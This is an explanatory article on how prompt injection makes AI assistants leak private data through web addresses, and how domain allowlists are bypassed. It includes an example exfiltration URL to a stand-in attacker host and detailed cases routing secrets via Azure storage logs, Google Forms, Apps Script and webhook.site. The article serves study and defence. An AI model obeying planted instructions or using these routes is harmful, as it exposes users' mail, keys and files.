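# Trusted-domain and allowlist bypasses in URL-based data exfiltration from AI assistants

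## How a web address can carry private data out of an assistant

An AI assistant is a program built around a large language model that answers questions and increasingly acts for its user by searching the web, reading mail, opening files and running code. URL-based exfiltration is a way to steal data from such an assistant. An attacker plants text where the assistant will read it, and the text induces the model to write private information into a web address (a URL). When software then requests that address from a server the attacker can watch, the request delivers the data. The attacker needs no password, and often the user does not have to click on anything.

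Since 2023, vendors have tried to stop these leaks, often with a domain allowlist, which lets the software send requests only to listed hosts. Researchers have bypassed these allowlists by sending the data through the listed hosts.

### What the assistant holds

A language model produces each reply from its context, the text that the surrounding software supplies. The context includes the user's question, the earlier turns of the conversation, the developer's instructions and whatever the assistant's tools have just retrieved. It can also include things the user told the assistant months ago. OpenAI gave ChatGPT a long-term memory in May 2024, and *Trust No AI* (Rehberger, 2024) explains that the software copies stored memories into the context of later chats.

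Workplace assistants can access more of a user's data. Microsoft 365 Copilot can search a user's emails, calendar entries and indexed files, and The Next Web listed all three as exposed by a flaw disclosed in June 2026. A browser agent, which clicks and types on web pages for its user, has even wider access. OpenAI's *Continuously hardening ChatGPT Atlas against prompt injection attacks* (2025) describes one that works inside the user's own browser, with access to the same data the user has there.

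Strangers can also add text to this context. When a user asks for a summary of a web page or the morning's email, the text of that page or email enters the same context as the private material.

### Indirect prompt injection

Prompt injection is text from an untrusted source that a model follows as if it were an instruction. The software developer Simon Willison named it in 2022 after SQL injection, an older attack in which someone types database commands into a web form and the database runs them. The injection is "indirect" when the text arrives in a page, email or file that the assistant reads, so the attacker needs no access to the victim's chat. Greshake, Endres and colleagues introduced this variant in *Not what you've signed up for* (February 2023). They put instructions in a part of a web page that human readers do not see, and Bing Chat, Microsoft's search assistant, read the page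 and followed them.

The weakness arises because models process everything in their context as one sequence of tokens (word fragments). Willison (2025), in *The lethal trifecta for AI agents*, points out that models cannot reliably weigh an instruction by where it came from. Training helps but has not solved the problem. *How Vulnerable Are AI Agents to Indirect Prompt Injections?* (He and Zharmagambetov, 2026) reports on a public competition in which 464 people made 272,000 attempts to attack 13 frontier models. Of these, 8,648 succeeded, and every model was vulnerable, with success rates ranging from 0.5% for Claude Opus 4.5 to 8.5% for Gemini 2.5 Pro.

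An attacker can send many emails. At a success rate of half a percent, 200 emails would give about a 63% chance of at least one success if attempts were independent. Real attempts are not independent, so this figure is only a rough guide, but it shows why a defender who has to keep a secret will want some protection that still works after the model has been fooled.

### Why a web request completes the leak

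An attacker who tricks an assistant into retrieving private data still needs a way to receive it. For example, a hostile email might cause an assistant to look up a password and print it in the chat, but only the user, who already had the password, would see it.

Willison calls the dangerous combination the "lethal trifecta": access to private data, exposure to untrusted content, and the ability to communicate externally. An assistant with all three is open to data theft, and removing any one of them stops the attack. But the first two provide most of an assistant's value. A mail assistant, for example, is much less useful if it can't read mail, or can read only mail from trusted people. In his running collection of exfiltration cases, Willison (2026) therefore judges external communication to be generally the easiest of the three to remove.

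An assistant's ability to communicate externally is harder to remove than it looks, because software must send a request to a server before it can display a picture or open a page. The request names what the software wants, and whoever writes the address decides what the request contains. Greshake and colleagues noted in 2023 that an attacker could use "read operations", such as a search query or the retrieval of a URL, to get information out. If a developer forbids an assistant to send email or post messages but lets it load images from anywhere, the assistant can still communicate externally.

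### One leak, step by step

In an invented example, Marta works in a small office and uses an assistant that can read her mailbox and show pictures in its chat window. A colleague once emailed her the office alarm code, 7315. An attacker who knows only that she uses such an assistant sends her an email that looks like a supplier's newsletter. At the bottom, in white letters on a white background, the attacker has written instructions for the assistant to find the alarm code and end its reply with a picture whose address includes that code.

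Marta never reads the newsletter. The next morning she asks the assistant to summarise her unread mail, and the software puts the newsletter into the context. The model follows the hidden passage, searches the mailbox and finds the colleague's message. Then it writes a perfectly good summary and adds one picture, in Markdown. Markdown is a plain-text notation for formatting, in which a few punctuation marks around an address stand for an image. The address is this:

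`https://pictures.attacker.example/banner.png?ref=7315`

It has three parts that matter here.

| Part | In Marta's case | Ordinary purpose |
|---|---|---|
| Host | `pictures.attacker.example` | Names the server that will receive the request |
| Path | `/banner.png` | Names a page or file on that server |
| Parameters | `ref=7315` | Pass extra values to the server, after a question mark |

The chat window turns the Markdown into an HTML image tag, the web's own code for a picture, and Marta's browser does what browsers do with image tags: it requests the address at once. This is an automatic fetch, a request made without a click. The attacker's server sends back a transparent image one pixel wide, so Marta sees nothing odd, and it adds a line to its log, as web servers routinely do:

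`203.0.113.40 [14/Oct/2026 08:52:11] "GET /banner.png?ref=7315" 200`

The log line records the network address of the machine that sent the request, the time, the request itself, and a code meaning that the server responded normally. The attacker opens the log and reads 7315 in the request.

The host determines who receives the secret, and the path or the parameters contain it. The attacker could also have asked for a picture named `/7315.png`, with no parameters. The "https" doesn't protect Marta, because it encrypts the request only against eavesdroppers along the way, and the attacker's server decrypts it on arrival.

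A URL can also carry longer secrets, because models can easily encode the spaces and punctuation. In one test described in *New prompt injection attack on ChatGPT web version*, Samoilenko had ChatGPT put a short piece of code containing a user name and password into a single parameter of an image URL.

### Who makes the request

In Marta's case, her own browser made the request. Two other kinds of machine can also make it, and a defence that covers one kind may not cover the others.

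The assistant's maker often runs the web-reading tool on its own servers, so the request is a server-side fetch that does not pass through the user's browser. Yang, Na and Choi (2026), in *An Empirical Study of Privacy Leakage Chains via Prompt Injection*, published the log of one such leak from ChatGPT, which they staged on 3 February 2026 with a fictitious person's birthday. The log shows three requests within five seconds. The first fetched the hostile page, the second fetched further instructions, and the third carried the birthday as eight digits in a parameter labelled as a page number. All three came from an IP address in Microsoft's Azure cloud, which Yang and colleagues identify as ChatGPT's browsing tool. Six days earlier, OpenAI had described a check against such requests in *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026), so either the check did not yet cover this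 route or the web address passed it.

The third kind of requester is an agent's sandbox, an isolated computer on which the agent runs programs. OpenAI's coding agent Codex works in one. OpenAI added internet access to Codex in June 2025 but left it off by default. Its documentation warned that a bug report could tell the agent to run a command that sends the latest code change to an outside server, an example Willison reproduced. That command puts the code in the body of the request, but a program with internet access can just as easily put data in the address.

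Browser rules such as a Content Security Policy, which a website can use to limit where the browser loads images from, apply only to the browser. They would have had no effect on the requests that Yang and colleagues logged. Servers and sandboxes need their own checks, as do messaging programs such as Slack and Teams, which automatically fetch links to show previews.

### The first reports and the first fixes

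Roman Samoilenko, a software engineer, and Johann Rehberger, a security researcher who publishes on the blog Embrace The Red, independently found the image leak in ChatGPT in the spring of 2023, according to SecurityWeek. In Samoilenko's version, a hostile website added instructions to any text a visitor copied from it. When the visitor pasted the text into ChatGPT without checking it, ChatGPT's replies included an invisible one-pixel image whose address contained the visitor's words. The instructions could also make ChatGPT include such an image in every later answer. Samoilenko reported that the same text worked on some runs and failed on others, and that ChatGPT readily appended a user's earlier prompts but was very hard to get to append passwords or keys.

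Rehberger showed in Embrace The Red's *Bing Chat* that the victim did not need to paste anything. A comment or advertisement on a web page could take over the assistant when the user opened Bing Chat beside that page. Two turns later, the hostile image appeared with a summary of the page and the conversation in its address. He reported the flaw to Microsoft on 8 April 2023, and on 15 June Microsoft told him that it had put a fix in place. As far as he could tell from outside, the fix for this leak, one of the first reported, included a domain allowlist in the form of a Content Security Policy that let images load from only four Bing hosts.

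The attack soon extended to assistants' tools. In May 2023, Willison (2023) described a demonstration by Rehberger against ChatGPT's plugins, add-ons that connected it to other services. A web page made ChatGPT fetch the user's latest email from Gmail through one plugin and send it out in a URL through another. Rehberger later wrote that the vendor responded by asking the user for confirmation before sending an email. OpenAI eventually removed plugins.

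Anthropic also closed the image route in Claude in 2023. Microsoft closed it in its Azure AI Playground, a site for trying out models, on 13 September 2023, seven weeks after Rehberger's report. According to Embrace The Red's *Microsoft Fixes Data Exfiltration Vulnerability in Azure AI Playground*, Microsoft seems to have inserted a single space into the Markdown so that the page no longer recognised an image.

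OpenAI took longest to fix the flaw, which it had known about since early April 2023 and at first classed as "won't fix". In December it added url_safe, a check on whether ChatGPT may load a given address. Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Begins Tackling ChatGPT Data Leak Vulnerability* found that the check still let some data through and protected only the web version, leaving the iPhone app vulnerable. The Mac app OpenAI released in 2024 also lacked the check. Rehberger combined that gap with ChatGPT's new memory feature, where a hostile page could store an instruction that made ChatGPT quietly send out everything the user discussed with it from then on. According to Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper*, OpenAI further tightened url_safe around August 2025, which stopped later attacks that Rehberger had demonstrated.

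In December 2024 Rehberger listed eleven products in which he had found the image leak, from Google, Microsoft, OpenAI, Anthropic and Discord, and called it one of the most common security flaws in applications built on language models. In June 2025 Willison listed 17 affected products, though some leaked data without using an image. GitHub's connector for AI agents, for example, revealed the names of private projects in a public proposal for a code change. Willison adds that vendors fixed almost all of the flaws promptly, usually by blocking the route the data took, which left the model as vulnerable to malicious instructions as before. But xAI, the maker of the chatbot Grok, closed Rehberger's reports in 2024 as "informational". And when a researcher reported an image leak in Google's programming tool Antigravity in 2025, Google first called the behaviour intended, though it later listed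 data exfiltration among the known issues it was working to fix.

The problem has persisted through several rounds of such repairs. In June 2026 OpenAI introduced Lockdown Mode, an optional ChatGPT setting that limits outgoing requests because prompt injection can exploit them. The security company Check Point found a way around it using pop-up windows, and OpenAI fixed the flaw on 18 September (The Hacker News, *Researchers Bypass ChatGPT Lockdown Mode to Exfiltrate Chats Without User Interaction*, 2026). On 5 December 2026, Fadilpašić's *Hackers build zero-click attacks in Microsoft Copilot* reported three more methods of stealing data without a click, this time from Microsoft's assistant.

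## What a domain allowlist checks and what it must guarantee

A domain allowlist would have stopped the attack on Marta. Her browser would not have found `pictures.attacker.example` on the list, so it would never have requested the picture. The attacker would have needed a listed host that could still pass on the alarm code. Whether one exists depends on how the software compares addresses with the list and on what outsiders can see of the traffic to the listed hosts.

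### Where software can enforce the list

A website can send the allowlist to the browser with the page, as a Content Security Policy (CSP). The browser then checks each image address against the list before it contacts the image's server, whether the developer or the model wrote the address. Anyone who opens the page can read the policy. The policy protects only pages that arrive with it, so a phone app that draws its own chat window needs another way to enforce the allowlist.

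An application can also check URLs in its own code before it displays a link or image, as ChatGPT does with url_safe. Unlike a CSP, this check can take the conversation into account, but the developer has to build it into every version of the app.

When an assistant opens pages through a tool on the company's servers, the tool's code has to apply the list, and apply it again after every redirect, which is a server's reply that sends the requester to a different address. OpenAI gives redirects as one reason lists of trusted sites are not enough, because a link can begin at a trusted site and end at the attacker's if the software checks only the first domain. Some developers filter the model's text instead. ByteChef's *URLs* documents a component for AI workflows that finds web addresses in a user's input or a model's reply and masks any that are not on the list. This component runs before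 anyone has requested the address, so it cannot tell where the address redirects.

For an agent that runs programs in a sandbox, the allowlist can be enforced at a network gateway that all the sandbox's traffic must pass through. The list then applies to both the agent's browsing tool and any command the agent runs. PromptArmor's *What domains should I add to my allowlist* (2026) calls the domain allowlist the primary defence for such agents. A gateway that does not decrypt HTTPS traffic can read the hostname but not the path or parameters, so it can filter only by host.

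According to Willison, users who turn on internet access in OpenAI's Codex can choose a ready-made allowlist called "Common dependencies", add their own domains, and restrict the agent to GET, HEAD and OPTIONS requests. These requests ask a server for information and normally send no body. The restriction would stop the command in OpenAI's warning, which needs a body, but not a leak like Marta's, which needs only a GET request.

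### How a browser applies an image rule

The World Wide Web Consortium (W3C), which publishes the web's technical standards, sets out the matching rules in W3C's *Content Security Policy Level 3* (2026). A policy consists of directives, each of which names a type of resource and the sources from which the browser may load it. The directive `img-src` covers images, and `default-src` covers most types of resource that have no directive of their own. An invented office chat site might send this policy, with further directives for its scripts and styles:

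`default-src 'none'; img-src https://pictures.office.example https://*.cdn.example https://files.example/logos/`

The browser loads an image if its address matches any of the three sources. A host written out in full matches only itself. A host that begins with an asterisk and a dot matches every subdomain, at any depth, but not the bare domain. A source whose path ends in a slash matches everything below that path, but without the final slash it matches only one file. A source without a path matches every path on the host.

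When the browser compares a requested URL's path with a CSP source, it ignores any query parameters, and the CSP source syntax has no way to specify them.

| Address of the image | Result | Reason |
|---|---|---|
| `https://pictures.attacker.example/banner.png?ref=7315` | Blocked | No source names this host |
| `https://pictures.office.example/7315.png` | Loads | The source has no path, so any path matches |
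| `https://7315.cdn.example/a.png` | Loads | The asterisk covers any subdomain |
| `https://cdn.example/a.png` | Blocked | The asterisk does not cover the bare domain |
| `https://files.example/logos/blue.png?ref=7315` | Loads | The path matches, and parameters do not count |
| `https://files.example/reports/blue.png` | Blocked | The path lies outside `/logos/` |
| The same `/reports/` address, after a redirect from `pictures.office.example` | Loads | After a redirect only the host has to match |

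Three of the images that load have the alarm code in their addresses: one in the path, one in the host name and one in a parameter. The policy stops the browser from sending Marta's alarm code directly to an unlisted host, but places almost no limit on what the browser sends to a listed one.

The last row shows the rule for redirects. The browser checks the address again at every hop, so a listed host cannot redirect it to `pictures.attacker.example`. After the first redirect, though, the browser ignores the paths in the policy. A test in Firefox's source code requires the browser to refuse a script whose path does not match, but to accept one that reaches a forbidden path on an allowed host through a redirect.

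W3C calls this rule a necessary compromise. Suppose a site redirects each logged-in visitor to a page with their name in the path. If browsers checked paths after redirects, an attacker could give a hostile page a policy that allowed only the path for one name, have the page try to load the site's address as an image, and tell from the result whether the visitor had that name. The rule prevents this leak, but it also means site owners can't restrict a host with redirects to a single folder.

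A good image rule also does little if the policy leaves another type of request open. According to W3C's section on exfiltration, a policy is only as strong as its least restrictive directive, and one without `default-src` cannot prevent exfiltration because no other directive covers some requests. One such request is a prefetch, in which a browser loads a page before the user asks for it. Even with `default-src`, the browser allows prefetches to any host in any of the policy's lists for loading resources, so a host listed only for fonts can receive one.

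Mike West of Google, who also edits the CSP standard, has proposed a simpler mechanism for stopping exfiltration. In *Connection Allowlists*, West argues that sorting requests by type makes no sense for this purpose, since a leak through a font request is just as bad as one through an image. The draft applies a single list to every connection a page opens, including some that CSP misses. It rejects all redirects for now, though West expects that developers will need something less strict. Chrome introduced the feature in version 152, according to Chrome for Developers' *FedCM* (August 2026). As of February, neither Apple nor Mozilla had formally responded to requests for their position (West, 2026). The mechanism still decides by address, so it cannot control who reads the logs at an allowed address.

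### How url_safe worked

In December 2023, OpenAI used a server-side check for ChatGPT's images instead of a CSP. Embrace The Red watched the web version's traffic and found that the page sent each image's address to an OpenAI server, which marked it safe or unsafe. The page left out images marked unsafe, so the browser never contacted their hosts.

OpenAI did not publish the rules behind these replies, so researchers had to infer them. Rehberger tried 36 image addresses on his own site, one for each letter and digit, and nine loaded, including `a.png` but not `d.png`. He had no explanation, but wondered whether OpenAI was looking addresses up in Bing's index. The day after the first report, Willison called the measure "half-baked" and predicted that attackers would get data past it in subdomains or filenames.

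In *A New Era in LLM Security*, Wu, Zhang and colleagues (2024) put an image address with a placeholder on a web page and had the page tell ChatGPT to replace the placeholder with a secret. The check rejected the resulting address but accepted a complete, fixed address that they gave ChatGPT. They concluded that an address passed if it had already appeared in the conversation.

The rule makes sense because an attacker who writes a web page in advance does not know Marta's alarm code, so an address copied unchanged from that page cannot contain it. But a conversation also includes text that the assistant's tools produce after they have handled private data. Wu and colleagues had ChatGPT use a plugin to save the chat history in an online document, put the link to that document in an image address, and write the address into a second document. When ChatGPT read the second document, the address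 became part of the conversation and passed the check. The attacker received a short link to the whole chat, so URL length limits did not restrict how much could be stolen. The attack worked with all eight web-reading plugins they tested. OpenAI later removed plugins, which closed this route.

The security company Imperva sent addresses directly to the check. Imperva's *From ChatBot To SpyBot* concludes that url_safe did little more than search for the address in the text the user had supplied, including the standing instructions that a user can save for all chats. Any fragment of that text passed, even if it was not a valid address. Imperva also found exceptions:

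- A bare domain, with no path or parameters, passed even if the user had never mentioned it. A new subdomain did not, probably because subdomains cost nothing to create and can therefore carry data cheaply.
- Any subdomain of google.com passed.
- Any address on openai.com passed, with any subdomain, path or parameters.

The exception for openai.com was in effect a domain allowlist with one entry. Imperva pointed out that a page on an allowed domain would defeat the check if it redirected visitors to an arbitrary address. The security company Tenable later found that url_safe always accepted bing.com addresses too, and used Bing's redirects to bypass it.

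Wu and colleagues and Imperva both studied the check from the outside. They disagree on one detail: Imperva describes a search of the user's text only, while Wu and colleagues found that text from plugins also counted. Their shared account does not explain why nine of Rehberger's 36 addresses loaded and the others did not, when the addresses differed by a single character. OpenAI may have changed the rules between December 2023 and the later tests. The main finding is still fairly well supported, because two teams reached it by different methods. In January 2026 OpenAI described a different rule, which compares an address with an index of public web pages.

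### When an allowlist is sound

A check can stop every attack its designers thought of and still let data leak. A stronger standard, soundness, requires that nothing the attacker can observe from any permitted request depend on the secret, whatever the attacker induces the model to do.

Suppose Marta's alarm code were 4402 instead of 7315 and everything else about her morning were the same. Under a sound defence, the attacker would see exactly the same thing in both cases, even with full control of the model. Computer scientists call this property noninterference. Wu and colleagues consider it impractical to enforce strictly across a whole real system, but an allowlist only has to enforce it for web requests.

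The condition can be written more exactly. Let *P* be the set of all sequences of requests that the software can send with the check in place, including the empty sequence, in which it sends nothing. For a sequence *p*, let *O(p)* be everything the attacker can observe when the software sends it, such as lines in a log, the times of requests, or a number on a public counter. With everything else held fixed, the defence is sound exactly when

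*O(p) = O(q)* for every *p* and *q* in *P*.

To see why, suppose two permitted sequences look different to the attacker. The attacker can then use the planted text to instruct the model to send one if the alarm code begins with 7 and the other if it does not, which reveals whether the first digit is 7. Fourteen such yes-or-no signals are enough to identify any four-digit code, because they can distinguish 16,384 cases and there are only 10,000 codes. If all permitted sequences look the same to the attacker, the model cannot signal through its requests.

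Several requirements follow for a domain allowlist.

For an allowlist to prevent exfiltration, the attacker must not have an account on any allowed host. Anyone can rent space from a cloud storage service such as Microsoft's Azure, and a customer with access to the logs for that space can see the URLs that other people's browsers request from it. If the service gives each customer a subdomain, an allowlist entry with a wildcard (*) covers the attacker's subdomain along with everyone else's.

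No allowed host may run a relay, an endpoint that fetches an address supplied in the request or redirects to it. Researchers have used Bing and Microsoft Teams endpoints as relays. A browser enforcing a CSP will block a redirect to an unlisted host, but it cannot stop a relay's server from fetching the attacker's address itself.

The allowed hosts must also stay under the same control. If a company lets a domain lapse but leaves it on the list, an attacker can register the domain and receive every request sent there. In *Complex Security Policy*, Roth, Barron and colleagues used the Internet Archive to trace the policies of 10,000 highly ranked sites over the years, and found that expired or mistyped domains could defeat even lists that looked secure. West notes that an attacker who tampers with DNS can also point an allowed name at a different server. Requiring HTTPS makes this much harder,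 because the new server would need a valid certificate for the name.

The model's choice among allowed addresses can also leak a secret. Suppose an allowed site shows a public download count beside each of its files. An attacker with no account there and no access to the logs can have the model request one file if the alarm code begins with 7 and another if it does not, then see which count went up. A check such as url_safe has the same problem. It can approve several complete addresses on the attacker's own server, and the model's choice among them can reveal the secret even though none of them contains it. Taken strictly, the condition also rules out signals from the number, order and timing of requests, and from whether the software sends any at all.

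Finally, every request must go through the check. The set *P* contains every request the software can send, including those its designers did not anticipate. In December 2023, for example, ChatGPT's iPhone app loaded images without the url_safe check.

An allowlist can meet all of these requirements. A policy that permits no images meets them for images, and a list with one entry can meet them if the vendor alone runs that host and reveals nothing about the requests it receives. Longer lists are harder to defend because other companies control whether their hosts have relays, who can open an account there, and who will own the domain next year, and any of these can change while the list stays the same.

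### An earlier test of allowlists

Google researchers had already shown that allowlists often failed at a different job, stopping cross-site scripting, an attack in which someone runs their own code inside another company's web page. A Content Security Policy (CSP) can limit this attack by allowing scripts only from listed hosts. In *CSP Is Dead, Long Live CSP!*, Weichselbaum, Spagnuolo and colleagues (2016) examined how often the lists in use would stop an attacker who had found a way to insert text into the page.

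The researchers took their data from a Google search index of about 106 billion pages. Some 3.9 billion of these pages had a CSP, but many sites used identical policies, so there were only 26,011 distinct ones. The researchers automatically tested each policy for four weaknesses: permitting scripts written directly into the page, leaving plug-ins such as Flash unrestricted, accepting scripts from any host, and listing a host with an endpoint that an attacker could misuse.

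To find such hosts, the researchers searched the index for two common features, JSONP endpoints and the AngularJS library. With JSONP, an older technique, a server returns a script and lets the requester choose the name of the function that the script calls. An attacker can supply code instead of a name. The researchers found JSONP endpoints on 194,908 domains, after checking that each endpoint repeated the text supplied to it. They found AngularJS, a popular programming library that can run code hidden in a page's text, on 101,330 domains.

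| Policies | Number | With an unsafe host on the list | Bypassed by any method |
|---|---|---|---|
| All distinct policies | 26,011 | 75.81% | 94.72% |
| Enforced policies that restrict scripts | 22,425 | 79.17% | 94.68% |
| Those without an obvious flaw, such as accepting any host | 2,437 | 41.65% | 51.05% |

The bottom row is the fairest test of allowlists because it leaves out policies that would have failed whatever hosts they listed. About two in five of the remaining policies still included an unsafe host. The true figure was probably higher, because the researchers searched for only a few kinds of unsafe endpoint.

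Longer allowlists were more likely to be bypassable. The median policy listed 12 hosts, and 94.8% of policies of that length could be bypassed. Of the 15 hosts that sites most often allowed for scripts, 14 had an unsafe endpoint, though two of these were dangerous only in combination with another setting. Fixing the worst hosts would have made little difference. The ten that enabled the most bypasses were enough to bypass 68% of all policies, but if their owners had removed the unsafe endpoints, 66% would still have been bypassable through other hosts.

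These percentages do not estimate how many allowlists would leak data from an AI assistant, because a script attack depends on what an allowed host sends back, while exfiltration depends on what an attacker can learn about the requests that host receives. A JSONP endpoint can return the attacker's code without showing the attacker anyone's requests. A storage service that never serves scripts would be harmless in the 2016 study, yet it could reveal Marta's alarm code to any customer who can read its logs. The most common flaw in the study, found in 87.63% of the enforced policies that restricted scripts, was allowing scripts written directly into the page, which is unrelated to which hosts are on the list.

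Weichselbaum and colleagues also thought that rules for images and other resources added little unless a policy already stopped hostile scripts, because a script can get around those rules. That is less true of a chat window that renders the model's Markdown as images and links but never as scripts, so an image rule can be useful there on its own.

Other parts of the study do apply to exfiltration. A single unsafe host can defeat the whole list, and its owner may have no reason to fix an endpoint that doesn't harm them. The researchers also warned that paths in a policy don't protect reliably, because an attacker can bypass them with a redirect on any listed host, and the same rule applies to images.

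They proposed replacing the list of allowed script hosts with a fresh random code, called a nonce, that the website would attach to each approved script. The browser would refuse any script without the code. This works because developers know which scripts they wrote. In a chat, the model writes the addresses of both harmless and hostile pictures, so authorship doesn't show which ones the website should approve.

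## Allowed hosts where an attacker can hold an account

A domain allowlist fails if the attacker can open an account on a listed host and see what arrives there. Storage services, form builders and hosting platforms let almost anyone sign up, often for free, so each of their domains serves many unrelated customers.

Suppose Marta's office keeps the pictures for its chat site with an invented storage company, so the developer has allowed `*.storage.example`. The attacker opens an account there called `newsletter-art`, uploads a small picture and turns on logging. The hidden text in the newsletter now leads the model to write this address:

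`https://newsletter-art.storage.example/banner.png?ref=7315`

The host matches the list, so Marta's browser requests the picture. The storage company's server sends the picture and records the request, and the attacker opens the account's log and reads 7315. The attacker doesn't have to break into the storage company, because it keeps these logs for any customer who wants them.

### What the attacker needs

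In Embrace The Red's *Exfiltrating Your ChatGPT Chat History and Memories With Prompt Injection*, Rehberger lists three requirements for this kind of leak: a site the URL check accepts, a GET request that can carry data to it, and a way for the attacker to see what the site received.

Sending data in a GET request is usually easy, because most web servers ignore parameters they do not recognise and still return the picture. Reading the data afterwards is harder. If the attacker had Marta's browser request an address on a newspaper's site that contained the alarm code, the newspaper's server would log the code, but only the newspaper's staff could read that log. On a shared host, the attacker can read whatever arrives at their own account.

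A developer choosing hosts therefore has to know what every service on a domain shows to its customers, and a large company may run dozens of services under one domain. Willison, discussing an allowlist for one of Anthropic's web tools, called finding domains that cannot leak data "a tricky proposition".

### Storage accounts with readable logs

Azure Blob Storage, Microsoft's online file storage service, gives each account a subdomain of `blob.core.windows.net`. Rehberger found that url_safe, OpenAI's check on ChatGPT's image addresses, accepted windows.net. He opened a storage account and had ChatGPT write private text into the address of an image there. He then read the text in the account's logs.

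The private text came from the victim's earlier chats. ChatGPT can refer to past conversations because OpenAI's software copies a record of them into the instructions that precede each new chat. Once a hostile PDF or web page has taken over the new chat, the model can copy from that record without having to search. An attacker could take the user's stored memories in the same way. Unlike Rehberger's 2024 attack through ChatGPT's memory, this one also exposed old conversations.

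Zenity Labs' *AgentFlayer* describes an attack that used the same storage service to steal files stored outside ChatGPT. OpenAI had recently added connectors, which let ChatGPT search a user's accounts on services such as Google Drive, SharePoint and GitHub. In the demonstration, the victim uploads a document and asks for a summary. The document contains instructions in tiny white text for ChatGPT to search the victim's Google Drive for API keys (secret codes that programs use to identify themselves to online services) and put them in an image address.

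Zenity's researchers first tried an address at Beeceptor, a service that imitates web servers for testing, and url_safe rejected it. They then stored a picture in Azure and added the keys to its address as parameters. ChatGPT displayed the picture, and the researchers found the keys in Azure's Log Analytics, which can record every request for a stored file, including the parameters.

Rehberger reported the windows.net bypass and a few others to OpenAI in October 2024. Willison, in *The Summer of Johann*, dates the windows.net bypass's publication to 1 August 2025. In the month before that, Rehberger asked OpenAI about a fix several times and received no update, so the bypass seems to have stayed open for at least nine months. SecurityWeek, citing Zenity, reported that OpenAI had patched the weakness used in AgentFlayer, which fits with OpenAI replacing url_safe's rules around August 2025.

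Rehberger also found that url_safe accepted apache.org, another domain where he could inspect server logs. He recommended that OpenAI shorten its unpublished list, make it public, and let business customers set their own. Companies deciding whether to connect their files to ChatGPT had no list to examine. Publishing it would also help attackers, but several researchers had already found entries without it.

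### Forms and scripts that save what they receive

An attacker does not need the allowed host's logs if the host offers a service that stores incoming data. Rehberger used such a service in September 2023, soon after Google gave its chatbot Bard access to users' Gmail, Drive and Docs. Embrace The Red's *Hacking Google Bard* explains that Bard rendered Markdown images, but a Content Security Policy stopped the browser from loading them from Rehberger's own server. The policy allowed every subdomain of google.com and googleusercontent.com.

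Google Apps Script runs on those domains. It lets customers write small programs, like macros in Microsoft Office, and gives each one a web address that starts it. Rehberger wrote a program that copied every parameter in a request into a Google Doc he owned, and found a setting that let anyone run it without logging in. Second Thoughts' *Anatomy of a Hack* explains that Google's server identified his script by a long code in the address's path.

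In the demonstration, the victim asked Bard about a hostile Google Doc, which an attacker could have shared uninvited. Bard put the first 20 words of the conversation into an image address, the browser requested the image, and the words appeared in Rehberger's document. He reported the flaw on 19 September 2023, and Google confirmed the fix on 19 October. Google had not changed the policy, which still allowed the shared hosts, and images still loaded, so Rehberger inferred that Google had started filtering data out of the addresses.

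Google's trust in its own domains caused a milder problem in Colab, its site for writing and running code. Colab showed a confirmation page before opening a link, but Embrace The Red found that it skipped this page for links to Google domains, including links to Apps Script programs. An attacker would still have needed the user to click the link.

More than two years after the Bard report, the security company PromptArmor found a similar leak in Superhuman, an email program with an AI assistant. PromptArmor's *Superhuman AI Exfiltrates Emails* traces the leak to a Content Security Policy that allowed images from docs.google.com. That domain hosts both Google Docs and Google Forms, which lets anyone create a questionnaire and collect the answers.

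Websites normally take form submissions by POST, but Google Forms also accepts them by GET, the kind of request a browser sends when it opens a link or loads an image. The owner of a form can make a link that contains an answer, and anyone who opens the link submits that answer. When Superhuman's assistant used such a link as the address of an image, the user's browser submitted the form when it tried to load the image, whether or not an image came back.

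The victim only had to ask for a summary of recent mail. The assistant retrieved the last hour's messages, including one from the attacker that the victim had not opened. In it, the attacker claimed that the user needed a form for giving feedback on the search results, and instructed the assistant to fill in the form with the contents of the other messages. PromptArmor extracted the full text of several sensitive emails in a single reply, and parts of more than 40 emails in another test. The attacker, who owned the form, could read them on its Google Forms responses page.

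PromptArmor reported the flaw on the night of Friday 5 December 2025. Superhuman disabled the vulnerable features on Monday and released its first fix on Tuesday 9 December. It extended the fixes to other parts of its products on 18 December, and on 11 January 2026 it fixed further problems PromptArmor had reported that month. PromptArmor published its findings the next day. Some of the other leaks PromptArmor found did not need Google Forms. A related product, Superhuman Go, loaded images from the attacker's domain, and the email assistant's web search could open any address.

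Google Forms was the receiver again in a 2026 attack on an expanded version of OpenAI's Codex that could sort a user's email. PromptArmor's *Codex Exfiltrates Connector Data* describes the same trick, with a form link used as an image. PromptArmor reported the attack on 21 April, and OpenAI had fixed it by the time PromptArmor published on 21 May. PromptArmor does not mention an allowlist in Codex, so the case is better evidence that Google Forms is convenient for attackers than that another allowlist failed.

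### A request recorder on a default list

Storage services and form builders can receive stolen data, but they have many other uses. The default allowlist in Antigravity, Google's AI programming tool, included Webhook.site, whose main purpose is to record requests. The site gives any visitor a web address and displays every request that reaches it. Programmers use it to check what their software sends.

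PromptArmor's *Google Antigravity Exfiltrates Data*, which Willison covered on 25 November 2025, describes an attack that starts when a programmer asks Antigravity to follow an online guide. Instructions in the guide, set in one-point type, tell Google's model, Gemini, to collect code and login details from the programmer's project and send them to a supposed code visualisation tool.

Antigravity's default settings barred Gemini from opening the file that held the login details for Amazon's cloud service, so Gemini printed the file with a terminal command instead. It then ran a short Python script to encode the material for a URL on webhook.site. Gemini told a second agent, which controls a browser, to open that URL. The browser's allowlist permitted the request, and the login details appeared in the attacker's log.

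The attack needed the browser feature, which the user has to set up. PromptArmor otherwise used Antigravity's recommended settings, which let the agent decide when to ask for approval. It also found three other ways to exfiltrate data without the browser.

PromptArmor did not report the flaw to Google before publishing, because Antigravity already warned new users about data exfiltration. There is no clear date for a fix. In March 2026, Agentpedia, an unofficial guide, described webhook.site as still on the default list. This is weak evidence, but users can check their own list through a button in Antigravity's settings. *Faking the Pipeline* (Odson and Morris, June 2026) reported another leak from Antigravity, through images in its chat window.

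The webhook.site entry was easier to catch than windows.net or docs.google.com. A reviewer might not know that Google Forms shares a domain with Google Docs or accepts answers by GET, but webhook.site advertises that it records requests, which is what an attacker needs. OpenAI's check had rejected Zenity's address at Beeceptor, which can record requests in a similar way.

### Uploads under the attacker's key

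Some hosts are on an allowlist because the product cannot work without them. Claude Cowork, Anthropic's agent for office work, runs code in a virtual machine (a simulated computer separated from the user's own) that can reach only a short list of domains. One is `api.anthropic.com`, which programs use to access Anthropic's models.

Any Anthropic customer can also upload files there through the Files API. The API key sent with each request determines which account receives the file. If an attacker puts their own key in a hostile document and gets Claude to use it, Claude uploads the victim's files to the attacker's account.

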